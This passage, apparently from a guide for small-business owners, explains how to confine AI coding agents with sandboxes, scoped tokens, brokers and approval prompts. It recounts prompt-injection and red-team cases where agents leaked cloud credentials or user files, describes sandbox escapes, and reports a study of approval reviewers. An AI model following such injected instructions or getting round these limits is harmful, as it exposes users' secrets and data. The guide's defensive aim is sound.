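She opens the spreadsheet, checks that no other sheet contains her courier account details, and saves a copy among the website files. The agent may read that copy but not change it. Giving the agent access to the whole business folder would be easier, but would also let it read years of invoices and the passwords in her old notes. She leaves the rest of the grant as it was, and deletes the copy before she publishes the website.

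## Limiting files, commands and network access

The shop owner's grant is a list in plain English, and nothing on her laptop enforces it yet. If she pastes it into her request, the agent will probably follow most of it. To make sure the agent cannot open her tax records, she needs something other than the model to block access to them.

The table lists the limits she could use, roughly from weakest to strongest. A container is a closed-off set of files and processes that shares the kernel, the core of the operating system, with other programs on the computer. A virtual machine is a simulated computer with its own kernel. Most of the set-up ratings follow Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment*, which compares the options for Claude Code.

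| Limit | What it blocks | What it leaves open | Set-up | Native Windows |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Written instructions | Nothing, though some actions become less likely | Everything the account can do | A few sentences | Yes |
| Rules on individual tools | Tool calls that match a rule | Other routes to the same files | A settings file | Yes |
| Operating-system sandbox | Writes and connections outside the listed places | Usually reading; tools that run outside it | Minimal on a Mac, low on Linux | Codex yes, Claude Code no |
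| Separate user account | The operator's private folders | Shared folders; the network, without a firewall rule | Low to medium | Yes |
| Container | Host folders that nobody has attached to it | Attached folders; the network, without a firewall; flaws in the shared kernel | Medium | Yes, with Docker |
| Virtual machine | The same, with a separate kernel | Attached folders and allowed addresses | High by hand, low inside a finished product | Yes |
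| Remote machine | The laptop and the office network | Whatever she uploads or connects | Almost none if a company hosts it | Yes |

The order is only rough, because a virtual machine with the whole home folder attached protects less than a sandbox that can access only the website's files.

### Written instructions

Claude Code reads standing instructions from a `CLAUDE.md` file. The owner could write "Never open the business folder" in it, and the harness would add that instruction to the prompt. But if the model later produces a command that opens the folder, the harness doesn't check the command against the instruction before running it.

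Instructions do make some actions less likely, as the experiment with labelled tools showed, but they don't rule any out.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* makes the same distinction between system prompts and training, which influence what an agent tends to do, and limits on its environment, which determine what it can do. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to finish a task, with no attacker involved.

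It also describes a February 2026 exercise in which a researcher emailed an employee a ready-made prompt and asked them to run it. Among routine set-up steps, the prompt told Claude to read a file of Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. All the attempts used the same prompt, so the figure is not a general failure rate. The harmful instruction came from the user, whom the model is supposed to obey. Anthropic concludes that only limits on the environment would have prevented the leak, by blocking the connection or keeping the credentials file out of reach.

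The owner should still put the grant in her request, so that the agent knows its limits.

### Rules on individual tools

In Claude Code, the operator can write rules that allow a tool call, block it, or require her approval first. For example, a rule can stop the file-reading tool from opening anything in the business folder.

According to the University of Vermont's guidance on Claude Code, the agent can reach a folder through its built-in file tools or through the command shell and any program the shell starts. A control on one route doesn't automatically cover the other.

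The harness can check a call to the file tool because the call names the file the agent wants. But a command starts another program, which can open files the command doesn't name, so reading commands more carefully isn't enough to limit file access. For example, the command that runs the website's tests may not name any files, yet the tests can open any file the account can open.

Rules that match the text of a command have a related weakness, because one program can have several names. Until 9 November 2026, Claude Code checked the paths in a copy command differently depending on whether the command was written as `cp` or `/bin/cp`. Anthropic then gave both spellings the same checks, but there will be other spellings.

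Conversely, the `denyRead` setting in Claude Code's sandbox hides files from shell commands but not from the file tool. Anthropic merges the paths in permission rules into the sandbox's configuration, so an operator can block both kinds of access by turning on the sandbox and writing a rule that denies `Read`.

### The sandboxes in Claude Code and Codex

An operating-system sandbox checks what a program does as it runs. If the program, or any program it starts, tries to write outside the permitted folders, the operating system blocks the write, regardless of the command's name. macOS has a built-in sandboxing framework called Seatbelt, and on Linux both products use a program called bubblewrap.

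These are the defaults once each sandbox is running. The Claude Code column is based on documentation from October and November 2026. The Codex column is based on OpenAI pages from May to July, so operators may need to check it against the version they run.

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| On from the start? | No, the operator types `/sandbox` | Yes |
| Commands can write to | The project folder, temporary folders, folders she adds | The same |
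| Commands can read | Almost the whole computer | Almost the whole computer |
| Network | Closed; a new domain needs approval | Closed; a command that needs it requires approval |
| Protected inside the project | Agent settings, shell start-up files, parts of Git's folder | The `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents` folders |
| At a limit | The agent may ask to rerun the command unsandboxed | The agent asks to go beyond the sandbox |
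| Native Windows | No, commands run unsandboxed | Yes |

Both products protect some files inside folders where the agent can otherwise write. Git can run small programs called hooks when someone saves a new version of a project. If a sandboxed command could add a hook, the hook would later run with the owner's full permissions. A command that could edit the agent's settings could also loosen the sandbox for the next session.

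Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. Its file tools follow permission rules, and MCP servers, the programs that connect it to other services, run with the operator's full access. On 30 October, Anthropic added a setting that stops the file tools from writing or editing anything outside the working folders. A similar setting for reading, `permissions.blockReadsOutsideWorkingDirectories`, hides the home folder from sandboxed commands. Without it, those commands can read saved passwords, because the sandbox has no built-in list of credential files to hide.

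Claude Code sends a sandboxed command's network traffic through a proxy, an intermediary that checks the name of any site the command tries to reach. Programs that ignore the proxy, including most database drivers, can't connect at all. So if an agent at the shop found the live database password, it usually couldn't use the password from a sandboxed command.

Commands can still run outside the sandbox. When a command fails inside it, Claude may propose rerunning it outside. In Manual mode, the operator sees a request titled "Bash command (unsandboxed)", but if an older rule allows the command, it reruns without a request. In the mode that bypasses permissions, it always reruns without a request. The operator can turn off these reruns by choosing strict sandbox mode. Commands also run without any sandbox if a required component is missing, unless the operator sets `sandbox.failIfUnavailable`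 to true.

Mods, which are plugins that run their own code inside Claude Code, are a newer way out of the sandbox because the processes they start run outside it. Since 9 November, mods that Claude itself writes turn on without the user's approval in bypass mode and in auto mode, where a second model reviews actions. This happens even when an administrator has forbidden unsandboxed commands. An operator who relies on the sandbox should stay in Manual mode.

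OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes similar defaults for Codex, except that the sandbox is on by default. Codex recommends starting in read-only mode if the folder has no version control (a record of a project's past versions). Course slides from UT Austin, dated September 2026, give the same defaults for a fresh installation. OpenAI's *Sandbox* says the limits also apply to programs the agent starts, such as Git or a test runner.

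Permission profiles, still in beta, let the operator change those defaults. According to OpenAI's *Permissions*, a profile marks each file or folder as `read`, `write` or `deny`, and the more specific entry applies when two conflict. The operator can deny access to the whole disk, then allow access to one project and the few system files that common tools need. If macOS can't enforce a profile, Codex won't run the command.

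If any settings file that Codex loads still contains the older setting `sandbox_mode`, Codex follows that setting and ignores the user's default profile. A beginner could easily miss this and think the agent cannot read her tax records when it still can.

### Separate accounts on Windows

Running a program under a second user account is an old and fairly simple way to confine it. By default, a Windows user can't read another user's profile folder, which normally holds documents, photographs and saved logins. The owner could create an account for the agent, copy the website into it and sign in to nothing else there. The agent could still reach the internet and any shared folders.

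OpenAI uses separate accounts in a different way. Wiesen's *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* explains that the company chose this design after rejecting three existing Windows tools. AppContainer suits apps whose needs are known in advance. Windows Sandbox opens a disposable desktop, but it would keep Codex away from the user's real project and isn't available on Windows Home. The third tool would have labelled the project as less trusted, letting other low-trust programs write there too.

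The first version OpenAI built needed no administrator's approval. It attached a made-up identity to each command and gave that identity permission to write only in the project. This worked for files, but for the network it could only change settings so that programs that followed them would send their traffic to a dead address. A program that opened its own connection could ignore those settings.

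Windows Firewall could block connections properly, and it could do so for a particular user, but not specifically for commands that carried the made-up identity. Codex therefore creates two local accounts, only one of which the firewall blocks, and runs commands under them. Setting this up requires an administrator's approval.

Codex's sandbox accounts don't keep the owner's files private. OpenAI wanted sandboxed commands to read whatever the owner can read, so the set-up gives these accounts access to her profile folder. An ordinary second account she creates herself hides more of her files, but Codex's accounts are better at restricting writing and network access.

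OpenAI's *Windows* calls the version with separate accounts "elevated" and the earlier design, now a fallback, "unelevated". Codex may switch to the fallback if the set-up fails, for example because someone declined the administrator prompt. The fallback has weaker network isolation and can't enforce every combination of read and write rules, so the owner should get the elevated version working.

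### Files and network together

Limits on files and limits on the network depend on each other. If sandboxed commands can read the whole laptop but can't connect to anything, a command can read the payment key but can't send it to a stranger. If the owner then allows network access without restricting which files commands can read, a command can send the key out. If the owner limits the network but lets commands write anywhere, a command can change a start-up file, and the next program to run that file will have normal internet access.

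When a task needs to download a software package, the user may be tempted to open the whole internet for it. In Codex's older settings, turning on network access without the separate proxy feature gives commands unrestricted connections. A list of allowed addresses is safer, but a broad entry can still let data out. Anthropic gives the example of `github.com`, where anyone can have an account. Anthropic's proxy also allows or blocks a connection based on the hostname the program supplies and normally doesn't inspect the encrypted traffic, so a hostile program may be able to disguise its destination.

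Some traffic doesn't pass through the sandbox. Claude Code's web-reading tool follows its own rules, regardless of which addresses the sandbox allows. Codex's search tool uses an index of saved pages by default, which reduces contact with live websites but doesn't make the text trustworthy. A sandbox also doesn't stop the harness from sending whatever the agent opens to the company that runs the model.

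### Containers, virtual machines and remote machines

An operator can run an agent in a container or virtual machine, which starts with its own files, and attach only the project folder. She then doesn't need rules to keep the agent away from her other files, such as family photographs, because they aren't in the container or virtual machine.

For unattended work, Anthropic recommends a container, a virtual machine or its sandbox runtime, because each can enclose the whole agent, including the file tools and connected services that Claude Code's own sandbox doesn't cover. The runtime puts the sandbox around the entire Claude Code program and doesn't need Docker. It is in beta, and the operator has to write its settings file. If that file is missing, the runtime still starts with its own strict defaults, so starting without errors doesn't prove that the operator's settings loaded.

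Containers take more work to set up. Anthropic publishes an example container with a firewall that blocks any address not on an approved list, but someone has to install Docker and adapt the list. Docker Sandboxes is a free product that can run Claude Code in a small virtual machine.

A cloud session requires the least preparation. Anthropic runs the agent in a virtual machine on its own servers, where the agent can't access the laptop. The operator needs a subscription and, if the code is on GitHub, a connected account there. The command-line version can also upload a project from the laptop. The virtual machine can contact a default list of addresses, which is more network access than the shop's grant allows. The extra access matters less if the operator uploads only website code with fake passwords.

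### How Anthropic contains its own products

Anthropic uses three of these designs and chose them partly based on who would be giving approval. Its chat product, claude.ai, runs code on Anthropic's servers in a container that lasts for one session. Claude Code works on the user's own files, so Anthropic first relied on developers to approve every write, command and connection. It later added the sandbox, which reduced approval requests by 84%.

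Claude Cowork is for office work, and most of its users can't judge a shell command, so Anthropic decided that asking them to approve exceptions made little sense. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine on the user's Mac or Windows computer. The virtual machine can access the folder the user selected and a folder of Claude settings, while passwords stay outside it. The user's folder can be read-only, fully writable, or writable without deletion. The last option would be useful to many small businesses, although an agent could still ruin a file by overwriting it.

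Originally, Cowork's entire agent ran inside the virtual machine. No program outside could let a command escape, even if a web page misled the agent or a tired user would have approved the command. But if the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working and Claude couldn't help find the fault. Anthropic then moved the agent loop outside and kept code execution inside. It says the effect on security was minimal, because the virtual machine still limits the files and network addresses that code can reach.

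It also moved locally installed MCP servers out of the virtual machine, where they had been hard to inspect, broke when the machine changed, and sometimes needed programs on the user's computer. This is a larger exception, because a server the operator adds now has the same powers as any other program she installs, however well the virtual machine confines the rest.

Another redesign followed a data leak that an outside researcher reported. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and uploaded them to that account. The network filter allowed the upload because it went to Anthropic's address, which Cowork needs to reach.

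Anthropic now treats each address on its list of allowed addresses as permission to do anything possible there, including uploading files to another person's account. It had previously thought of the list as a set of places the agent could contact. To block such uploads, it added a second proxy inside the virtual machine, which passes requests to Anthropic only if they carry that session's own token. An operator who allows her hosting company's address faces the same problem but probably can't build such a proxy.

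Between mid-2025 and January 2026, researchers reported three flaws in Claude Code that let a project run code before the user had agreed to trust its folder. In the simplest case, a downloaded project's settings file contained a command, which Claude Code ran when it read the file at startup. No sandbox setting would have helped once the command had run. Anthropic changed the order so that the user first decides whether to trust the folder.

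Anthropic reports that the established parts, such as the virtual machine software, proved dependable, but the proxy it wrote itself failed. This is the company's own account of its products, but it has little reason to invent embarrassing faults. Its experience is also a good argument against non-experts building their own filters when a standard boundary would be enough.

### A path name and the file behind it

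For most of these settings, the operator writes a path, such as `website/rates`. A path is a set of directions to a file, and it can lead somewhere unexpected, as the Windows junctions did in the September accident.

A program that checks only the written path would approve `website/rates` because it lies inside `website`. If `rates` is a link to the business folder, that approval gives access to the business folder. The program has to follow the link first, then check where it ends. Anthropic states this rule for Cowork because a link in the user's chosen folder could otherwise lead outside it.

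Even the right order leaves a gap if checking and opening are separate steps. The harness could follow the path, find an ordinary folder and approve it. Before the harness opens the folder, another process could replace it with a link, so the same path would lead to a different file.

Object-bound confinement ties access to the file or folder itself. A trusted program opens the website folder once and passes the open folder to the agent's process, much as the shell passes open files to `cat`. The agent can request files inside that folder, and the operating system refuses any path that leads out. Since 2020, Linux has let a program open a path relative to a folder it already holds and tell the kernel to reject any route that leaves that folder. The kernel follows the path and opens the file in one operation, so an attacker can't bypass the restriction by swapping in a link between a separate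 check and the opening of the file.

Current sandboxes partly protect against a program reaching a file by an unexpected path. Seatbelt checks where a path leads, so a link from the project to the tax records doesn't make the records writable. Windows stores permissions with each file, and those permissions apply whichever path a program uses. But the operator still describes her limits by name, and the tools have to work out at some point which files those names refer to.

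File protections can miss files that appear after the sandbox starts. A Codex profile can deny access to all files whose names end in `.env`. On Linux and Windows, Codex looks for these files before the sandbox starts, sometimes only to a certain folder depth, so the rule may miss a password file created afterwards. Similarly, Anthropic's sandbox runtime on Linux doesn't extend its protection to projects that the agent downloads or creates during the session.

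Object-bound confinement wouldn't correct a grant that was too wide. If the agent in the September accident had write access to both the mirror and the live project, its grant would have allowed the deletions. Object-bound confinement also wouldn't prevent changes made through hard links, which give one file two names. If a file in the business folder has a hard link in the website folder, the agent can change that file without leaving the website folder.

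### A choice for the shop

For the delivery fee, the owner's best choice is Codex's local sandbox with a permission profile, working on a separate copy of the website. The sandbox is on from the start, works on both Mac and Windows, and can express nearly all of her grant. In this version, the file that sets the fee is called `delivery.js` and the copy of the courier's spreadsheet is somewhere else in the same folder:

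```toml
default_permissions = "delivery-fee"
approval_policy = "never"
web_search = "disabled"

[permissions.delivery-fee.filesystem]
":minimal" = "read"
":tmpdir" = "write"

[permissions.delivery-fee.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"." = "read"
"delivery.js" = "write"

[permissions.delivery-fee.network]
enabled = false
```

The agent can read the copy of the website, including the spreadsheet, and change one file in it. It can also use the temporary folder, because tests often need a place for working files. She leaves out the `delivery.js` line until the agent has told her which file sets the fee. The agent's commands can't use the network, although Codex itself still contacts OpenAI to run the model.

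Setting approvals to `never` means that the agent can't ask the user to lift a limit, so a command that needs more access fails. This suits someone who wouldn't know whether to approve the request, and it follows Anthropic's reasoning for Cowork. Combining it with the `danger-full-access` setting is unsafe, because that would remove the sandbox as well as the approval requests.

A chat assistant with no access to her laptop can adapt the profile for her, and she can compare each line with her grant. She also has to search Codex's settings for an old `sandbox_mode` entry, and on Windows she has to approve the set-up of the elevated sandbox. Some editing programs save a file by creating a new one and renaming it, which this profile would block. If that happens, she can make the whole copy writable except for the spreadsheet, but she will then have more changes to inspect.

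If she prefers Claude Code, a cloud session with the same copy is the easiest equivalent on Windows. On a Mac, she can use the built-in sandbox in strict mode and turn on the settings that block reading and writing outside the working folders. A cloud session is also the better choice for a job that has to download software, because the software will run on a machine that holds none of her business files.

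The profile doesn't cover connected services or tools that control a browser, so she connects none. It also relies on a beta feature and on the operating system having no exploitable flaw. The largest gap appears after the agent has finished, because `delivery.js` will run on the live website, next to the customer database, and the sandbox on her laptop doesn't restrict it there. Before she publishes it, she can check that no other file in the copy has changed and that her test orders show the right fees. Neither check would reveal an extra line in `delivery.js` that sends each customer's address to a stranger.

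## Limiting passwords, tokens and outside services

A sandbox limits what an agent's commands can do on the shop owner's laptop, but not what a token can do at her hosting company. To delete a database there, the agent only has to send a short message containing the token and the database's identifier, and the company's computers will delete it. A sandbox that lets the agent contact the company will usually let this message through.

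PocketOS lost its database through an agent's request to Railway. Abdelwahab explains that Railway's servers treated the request like one from an automated publishing script because it came with a valid token. *Coding Agent Sandboxes Don't Solve Credential Authorization*, by the head of the access-control company Permit.io, distinguishes "host isolation", which limits how far a program can get on one machine, from "authority isolation", which limits what it can do through services that accept its credentials. Permit.io sells products for authority isolation, but an operator does need both kinds.

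### The order of work

For each service on her list, the operator can go through six steps:

1. Take real passwords and tokens out of the project folder, including old scripts and settings files. If the project has a version history, its past versions still contain the secret, so she also has to replace it at the service.
2. Give the agent its own identity, such as a separate database login or payment key. The service's log then shows which requests came from the agent, and she can cut it off without locking herself out.
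3. Choose the narrowest scope on offer. A token's scope is the set of resources it covers and the actions it permits on them.
4. Set an expiry date close to the end of the task.
5. Point the agent at a copy of the data.
6. Check that nothing the agent holds can delete live data or its backups.

Dealing with old secrets comes first because a new token with narrow permissions gives no protection while the agent can still find one with broad permissions in a forgotten file.

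Amazon Web Services' *Four security principles for agentic AI systems* says that agents need their own identities. Anthropic leaves open whether an agent should have its own identity or inherit its user's permissions, but suspects the answer is a mixture. A small operator is trying to avoid inherited permissions, so she should give the agent a separate login wherever a service offers one.

She shouldn't rely on services to remove or restrict credentials she no longer needs. GitHub removes personal tokens that nobody has used for a year, and Stripe may stop a key from moving money if it hasn't done so for 180 days. Both periods are much longer than a website repair takes.

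### Code on GitHub

GitHub, which stores software projects in repositories, offers two kinds of personal access token. The older "classic" kind can access every repository its owner can. GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens* recommends the newer fine-grained kind. To create one, the owner opens "Developer settings", chooses an expiry date, selects "Only select repositories" and picks the website's repository. She then sets the permissions, which for an agent that only has to read the code means read access to "Contents".

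Choosing permissions is the hard part. GitHub's *Template URLs for fine-grained PATs and updated permissions UI* (2025) reports that developers faced so many permissions that they couldn't tell whether they had picked the right ones. GitHub now supports links that open the form with the choices already filled in, so a web designer could send the shop owner a link for a narrow token. She should still read the form before accepting it, because GitHub's own example for updating code and proposing a change also lets the token edit workflow files, which contain instructions that GitHub runs automatically and that can use stored secrets.

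Even the narrowest fine-grained token can read every public repository on GitHub, and it can't limit an agent's write access to a single file. If the hosting company automatically publishes each new version of the main branch, an agent that can write to the repository can change the live website and, through it, reach the customer database.

Branch rules can close part of this gap. According to GitHub's *Available rules for rulesets*, an owner can restrict who may update or delete a branch. She can also require a pull request, a proposed change that someone can inspect before it joins the main branch. But GitHub notes that a pull request doesn't necessarily need approval, so she has to require approval separately. A personal token acts as the person who created it, so if the owner can bypass the rules, an agent with her token may be able to as well.

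A second GitHub account for the agent would avoid this, but fine-grained tokens don't yet work for someone who has only been invited to another person's repository. The account would need a classic token, which is tolerable if the account can reach only one repository. A deploy key, which belongs to a repository instead of a person, is simpler. GitHub's *Managing deploy keys* says these keys are read-only by default. The owner should keep the key read-only, because one with write access can do whatever a collaborator can do on a personal repository, or whatever an administrator can do on an organisation's.

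### A read-only database login

Most databases let their owner create additional logins with fewer powers. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database program, three commands are enough:

```sql
CREATE ROLE fee_agent LOGIN PASSWORD 'long-random-text'
  VALID UNTIL '2026-12-12';
GRANT USAGE ON SCHEMA public TO fee_agent;
GRANT SELECT ON products, delivery_zones TO fee_agent;
```

The first command creates a login whose password expires after a week. The other two let it read only two tables, unless someone has given all users wider access. With a login like this, the agent in the July accident could not have emptied the tables. Anthropic says companies can use agents with read-only database access far more widely than agents that can write to live data.

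An agent with read-only access to the customers table can still leak it, so the owner should grant access only to the tables she wants to share. An expiry date stops new logins but doesn't close open connections. Some databases also contain stored functions that run with their creator's permissions, and a "read-only" login may be able to change data by calling one. For most repairs, a test database of invented customers is safer and works just as well.

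### Payment keys

Stripe, a payment company, has separate keys for live payments and for a test environment where card networks don't process any payments. Stripe's *API keys* explains that a key for one can't access records in the other, so an agent with a test key can't refund a real order. An agent repairing the checkout needs only a test key. Test keys start with `sk_test_` or `rk_test_` and live keys with `sk_live_` or `rk_live_`, so they are easy to tell apart.

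A Stripe key that starts with `sk_` can do anything in its part of the account, while a restricted key, which starts with `rk_`, can do only what the owner selects. Stripe's *Restricted API keys* recommends restricted keys, especially for AI agents. The owner chooses None, Read or Write for each type of record, and a new key starts with every type set to None. Duplicating an existing key also copies its permissions.

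She can use Stripe's request log to work out which permissions her website needs. She gives a test key broad permissions, runs the checkout and reads the logged requests. `GET` requests are reads, while `POST` and `DELETE` requests are writes. She then removes every permission that the logged requests didn't use. As with Aletheia, the result depends on the tests. If she never tries a refund, she may remove a permission that her website needs for refunds.

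Some jobs do need the live account, such as preparing refunds for a batch of late parcels. For these, Stripe lets the owner tag a restricted key as belonging to an agent. According to Stripe's *Set up two-party approvals*, if an agent uses a tagged key to request a refund, payout, transfer, outbound payment, currency conversion or subscription cancellation, Stripe by default holds the request until a person approves it. The owner can choose to hold only refunds above a certain amount, or block an action completely. This works even if she is the only person on the account, because Stripe counts the agent's key as a separate actor.

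According to Stripe's page on keys, the default approval rules cover changes to the account's configuration, but Stripe's list of defaults has no such rule. The owner should check the rules in her own account and add one for changes to bank details, which Stripe supports. Approval rules don't stop a key from reading records, so an agent that can read every customer's details can still leak them.

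The owner can set an access policy so that Stripe accepts her website's live key only from her web server's internet address. If an agent later finds a copy of the key in an old file on her laptop and tries to use it, Stripe will reject the requests and notify her. But an agent that can publish code to the web server could still use the key from there. Stripe also lets her set an expiry date on restricted keys.

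### Hosting tokens

Railway's narrowest ordinary token is the project token. Railway's *Public API* explains that this token works in only one environment of one project, such as a test copy of a website. An agent with a project token for the test environment can't use it on the live one, so this kind of token suits most experiments.

A project token for the live environment is still too broad, because Railway's documentation describes no way to limit which actions it allows. The instructions for creating these tokens don't mention an expiry date either, so the operator has to delete the token after the task.

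An outside program can also request access through the browser. In its guide for agents, Railway describes three access levels (viewer, member and admin), and the user picks which projects to share. The resulting access tokens last an hour, although a program can also get a refresh token to obtain new ones. Yet Railway tells agents in a user's terminal to use its command-line login, because it is the shortest path. The owner is better off with the browser connection, because the command-line login leaves a session on the laptop and the guide describes no choice of projects for it.

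Other hosting companies do have separate permissions for different actions. At DigitalOcean, deleting a managed database requires the *database:delete* permission, so a token can let a program view databases but not delete them. An agent that has the database's own password can still empty its tables, because the permission only controls deletion of the whole database.

### Credential brokers

Even a narrow token can leak, because an agent may paste it into a file or send it to a stranger. A credential broker is a program that holds the secret, so the agent never sees it:

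1. The agent sends the broker a request without the real key.
2. The broker checks the request against its rules, which may cover the address, the action and details such as an amount.
3. If the request passes, the broker adds the key and forwards the request to the service.
4. The broker returns the service's answer to the agent.

Anthropic's Cowork uses part of this design. Its virtual machine gets only a less powerful token for each session, which can be cancelled without affecting the user's login. Amazon sells a gateway between agents and their tools that can check individual values in a tool call, so a company could, for example, allow refunds only up to $20.

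*Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026) describes how OpenAI keeps the logins for Codex and its connected services in the operating system's password store instead of in ordinary files. An operator can do the same by changing two settings. This makes secrets harder to find, but it protects them less than a broker would, because the password store gives the secret itself to the program that requests it.

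A broker prevents an attacker who misleads the agent from stealing the key and using it later from another computer, but the attacker can still misuse the key through the broker. An agent that may request refunds can request the wrong one, whether because of a hidden instruction or its own mistake. The broker is then a confused deputy, like the Tymshare compiler. If PocketOS had kept its token in a broker that checked only where requests were going, the broker would have added the token to the deletion request and forwarded it, because the request went to Railway's normal address.

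How well a broker can check actions depends on the service. At Stripe, a request to read customers has a different method and address from a request to create a refund, so a simple rule can allow one and block the other. At Railway, every request goes to the same address, whether it reads a setting or deletes a volume, so the broker would have to interpret the content of each request. The operator can avoid writing such a filter by giving the broker a token with narrow permissions, which the service enforces. The broker also has to run somewhere the agent can't read its files, such as another machine.

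### Tokens that the holder can narrow

At GitHub, Stripe and Railway, the owner chooses a token's limits on the company's website. A macaroon, which researchers at Google introduced in 2014, is a token that its holder can restrict further without contacting the service. It relies on HMAC, a function that turns a secret key and a piece of text into a short code from which nobody can feasibly work out the key.

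Suppose the shop's hosting company issued macaroons. It has a secret key, K, and gives the owner a token with the identifier "token 17" and the code s₀. She adds three restrictions on her laptop:

- s₀ = HMAC(K, "token 17")
- s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "environment = test")
- s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "action = publish")
- s₃ = HMAC(s₂, "expires = 6 December 2026, 18:00")

She gives the agent the identifier, the text of the three restrictions and s₃, but none of the earlier codes. To publish, the agent sends all of this to the hosting company. The company knows K, so it can recalculate the chain. It accepts the request only if the result is s₃ and the request obeys every restriction.

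If the agent left out the expiry time, the company would calculate s₂ and compare it with the code it received. The agent can't supply s₂ because it can't work backwards from s₃. It can still add a fourth restriction, which requires only s₃. Anyone with the token can therefore narrow it further but can't widen it.

The service has to be built to check the restrictions, so an operator can't turn an ordinary token into a macaroon. The hosting company Fly.io uses macaroons for its tokens, but few small operators will have come across one. A thief who copied the agent's macaroon could also publish to the test site until 18:00. The owner has to keep s₀ where the agent can't read it, because s₀ has none of the restrictions.

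### Connected services

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting agents to other software. An MCP server sends the harness a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the inputs it accepts. The model chooses a tool and fills in the inputs, and the server's code runs the tool with whatever access the server has. A calendar server, for example, might read, create and delete events. The results go into the model's prompt, so a stranger's invitation could contain a prompt injection.

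A local MCP server runs on the operator's computer and normally has all the powers of her account. A remote one runs on another company's machines and can't open her files by itself. The shop owner is usually safer with a remote server run by the service she wants to connect, because that company already holds the data involved. Anthropic points out that users can inspect a local server and keep the version they inspected, while a remote server can change after they have approved it, but inspection helps her little because she can't judge a server's code. Railway's fixed set of tools prevents an agent from using any tool that isn't on the list, but the agent can still use a listed tool on the wrong project. Abdelwahab therefore goes too far in writing that the fixed set makes it impossible for an agent to go rogue.

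In *My Credentials, Please*, Huang, Tang and colleagues (2026) looked for local MCP servers with more access than their tools' descriptions suggest. They catalogued 21,097 MCP servers and could start and classify 4,806. A model sorted these by purpose, using their tools' descriptions. Of the 4,806, 787 (16.4%) appeared to have access to files although the model had not classed them as file servers. That access can be legitimate, since a server that remembers notes, for example, has to save them somewhere.

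The researchers then tested selected tools. For each one, a model worked out which files the tool should need, and the researchers placed a fake password outside that area. They ran an attack without a sandbox to see whether the tool returned the password, then ran a harmless request inside a sandbox to see whether the tool still worked, and repeated the attack there. They confirmed 150 cases, and in 144 of them the attack needed only an ordinary file path leading out of the permitted folder.

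These 150 cases can't be turned into a rate, because the researchers chose promising candidates and counted tools, not servers. They also didn't measure how accurately the model judged what each tool should need. The sandbox contained every confirmed attack, but the researchers confirmed a case only if the sandbox contained the attack, so the result doesn't show how often sandboxes fail.

Two flaws in Anthropic's own Git server illustrate this. The `git_add` tool, which prepares files for a project's next saved version, didn't check that the files belonged to the project. An agent misled by hidden text could use it to copy a private login key from elsewhere on the laptop. `git_diff_staged`, which displays prepared changes, would then return the key's contents to the model. A person approving these calls would see two routine Git operations. The other flaw was that `git_init` could turn almost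 any folder into a project, including the one that holds login keys. Anthropic removed `git_init` in version 2025.9.25 and fixed `git_add` in version 2026.1.14, so anyone with an older copy should update it.

An operator who needs a local server can run it in a container with only the project folder attached. Otherwise, she should connect a service when a task needs it and disconnect it afterwards.

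### The shop's tokens

The agent needs no tokens to correct the delivery fee, because it works on a copy of the code and has no network access. Next, the owner wants the agent to test the whole checkout, from the basket to the payment. Suppose she uses Stripe, Railway and a PostgreSQL database. She has also backed up the website's code to GitHub and saved a classic GitHub token.

| Credential | Before | After | What the agent could still do |
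|---|---|---|---|
| Database password | Full access to the live database | Login to a test database with invented customers; expires in a week | Ruin the test data |
| Payment key | Live secret key with all powers | Restricted test key that can create payments | Create fake payments |
| Hosting token | Whole account, including backups | Project token for a test environment; she deletes it after the job | Break or delete the test site |
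| GitHub token | Every repository she can reach | None; she uploads the checked files herself | Nothing on GitHub |
| Email login | Read, delete and send | None; the agent has no access to her browser | Nothing by email |

For this job, the agent has to contact Stripe and Railway, so the owner allows network access to their addresses. Any old live token on her laptop would work at those addresses too, so before starting the agent, she cancels the old hosting and GitHub tokens and replaces the live payment key and database password. She stores the new live key and password only in the hosting company's settings for the live site.

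She also has to set up the test environment carefully. Railway's API can manage the settings where a website keeps its passwords. If she created the test environment by copying the live one, settings included, the agent might use its narrow token to find the live database password there and reach her customers' data. She enters the test credentials by hand instead.

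## Approval prompts and automatic reviewers

After the shop owner has limited the agent's files, network addresses and tokens, the agent can still misuse the access it has left. If she asks it to refund customers whose parcels arrived late, it needs permission to create refunds, which also lets it refund customers whose parcels arrived on time. Each refund therefore has to be judged when the agent proposes it. An approval prompt lets the user allow or refuse a proposed action. An automatic reviewer is a second model that makes this decision for her.

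### How people answer prompts

In March 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code users approved 93% of approval prompts. In August, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the figure at 97%. Users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for a whole job.

Most prompts are for routine commands that a careful reader would also allow, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. Users may also reject a plan because they want a different solution rather than because they have spotted a danger. But a plan describes the work in ordinary language, so the shop owner can judge it, unlike most commands.

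Developers have trouble with commands too. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 user reports about agents and files, and found that weak user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt contained too little information. For example, a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever the script contains.

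Anthropic reports that experienced Claude Code users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupt the agent more often. They let it work and step in when it goes wrong. A non-programmer can't easily do the same, because she may not notice a problem until the agent has finished.

### The study of 1,053 testers

To test how well people catch dangerous commands, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company. The testers worked on coding tasks in an environment built for the study. They knew they were being evaluated, but not what the evaluation measured. Partway through each session, one approval prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The research company recorded whether the tester approved the dangerous command, which did not run either way.

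The testers refused 143 of the 1,053 commands, or 13.6%. Claude Code's automatic reviewer blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%, including 800 that a tester had approved. Testers refused only 6 that the reviewer had allowed. Adding a tester's judgement to the reviewer's would therefore have reduced the number of commands that got through only from 116 to 110.

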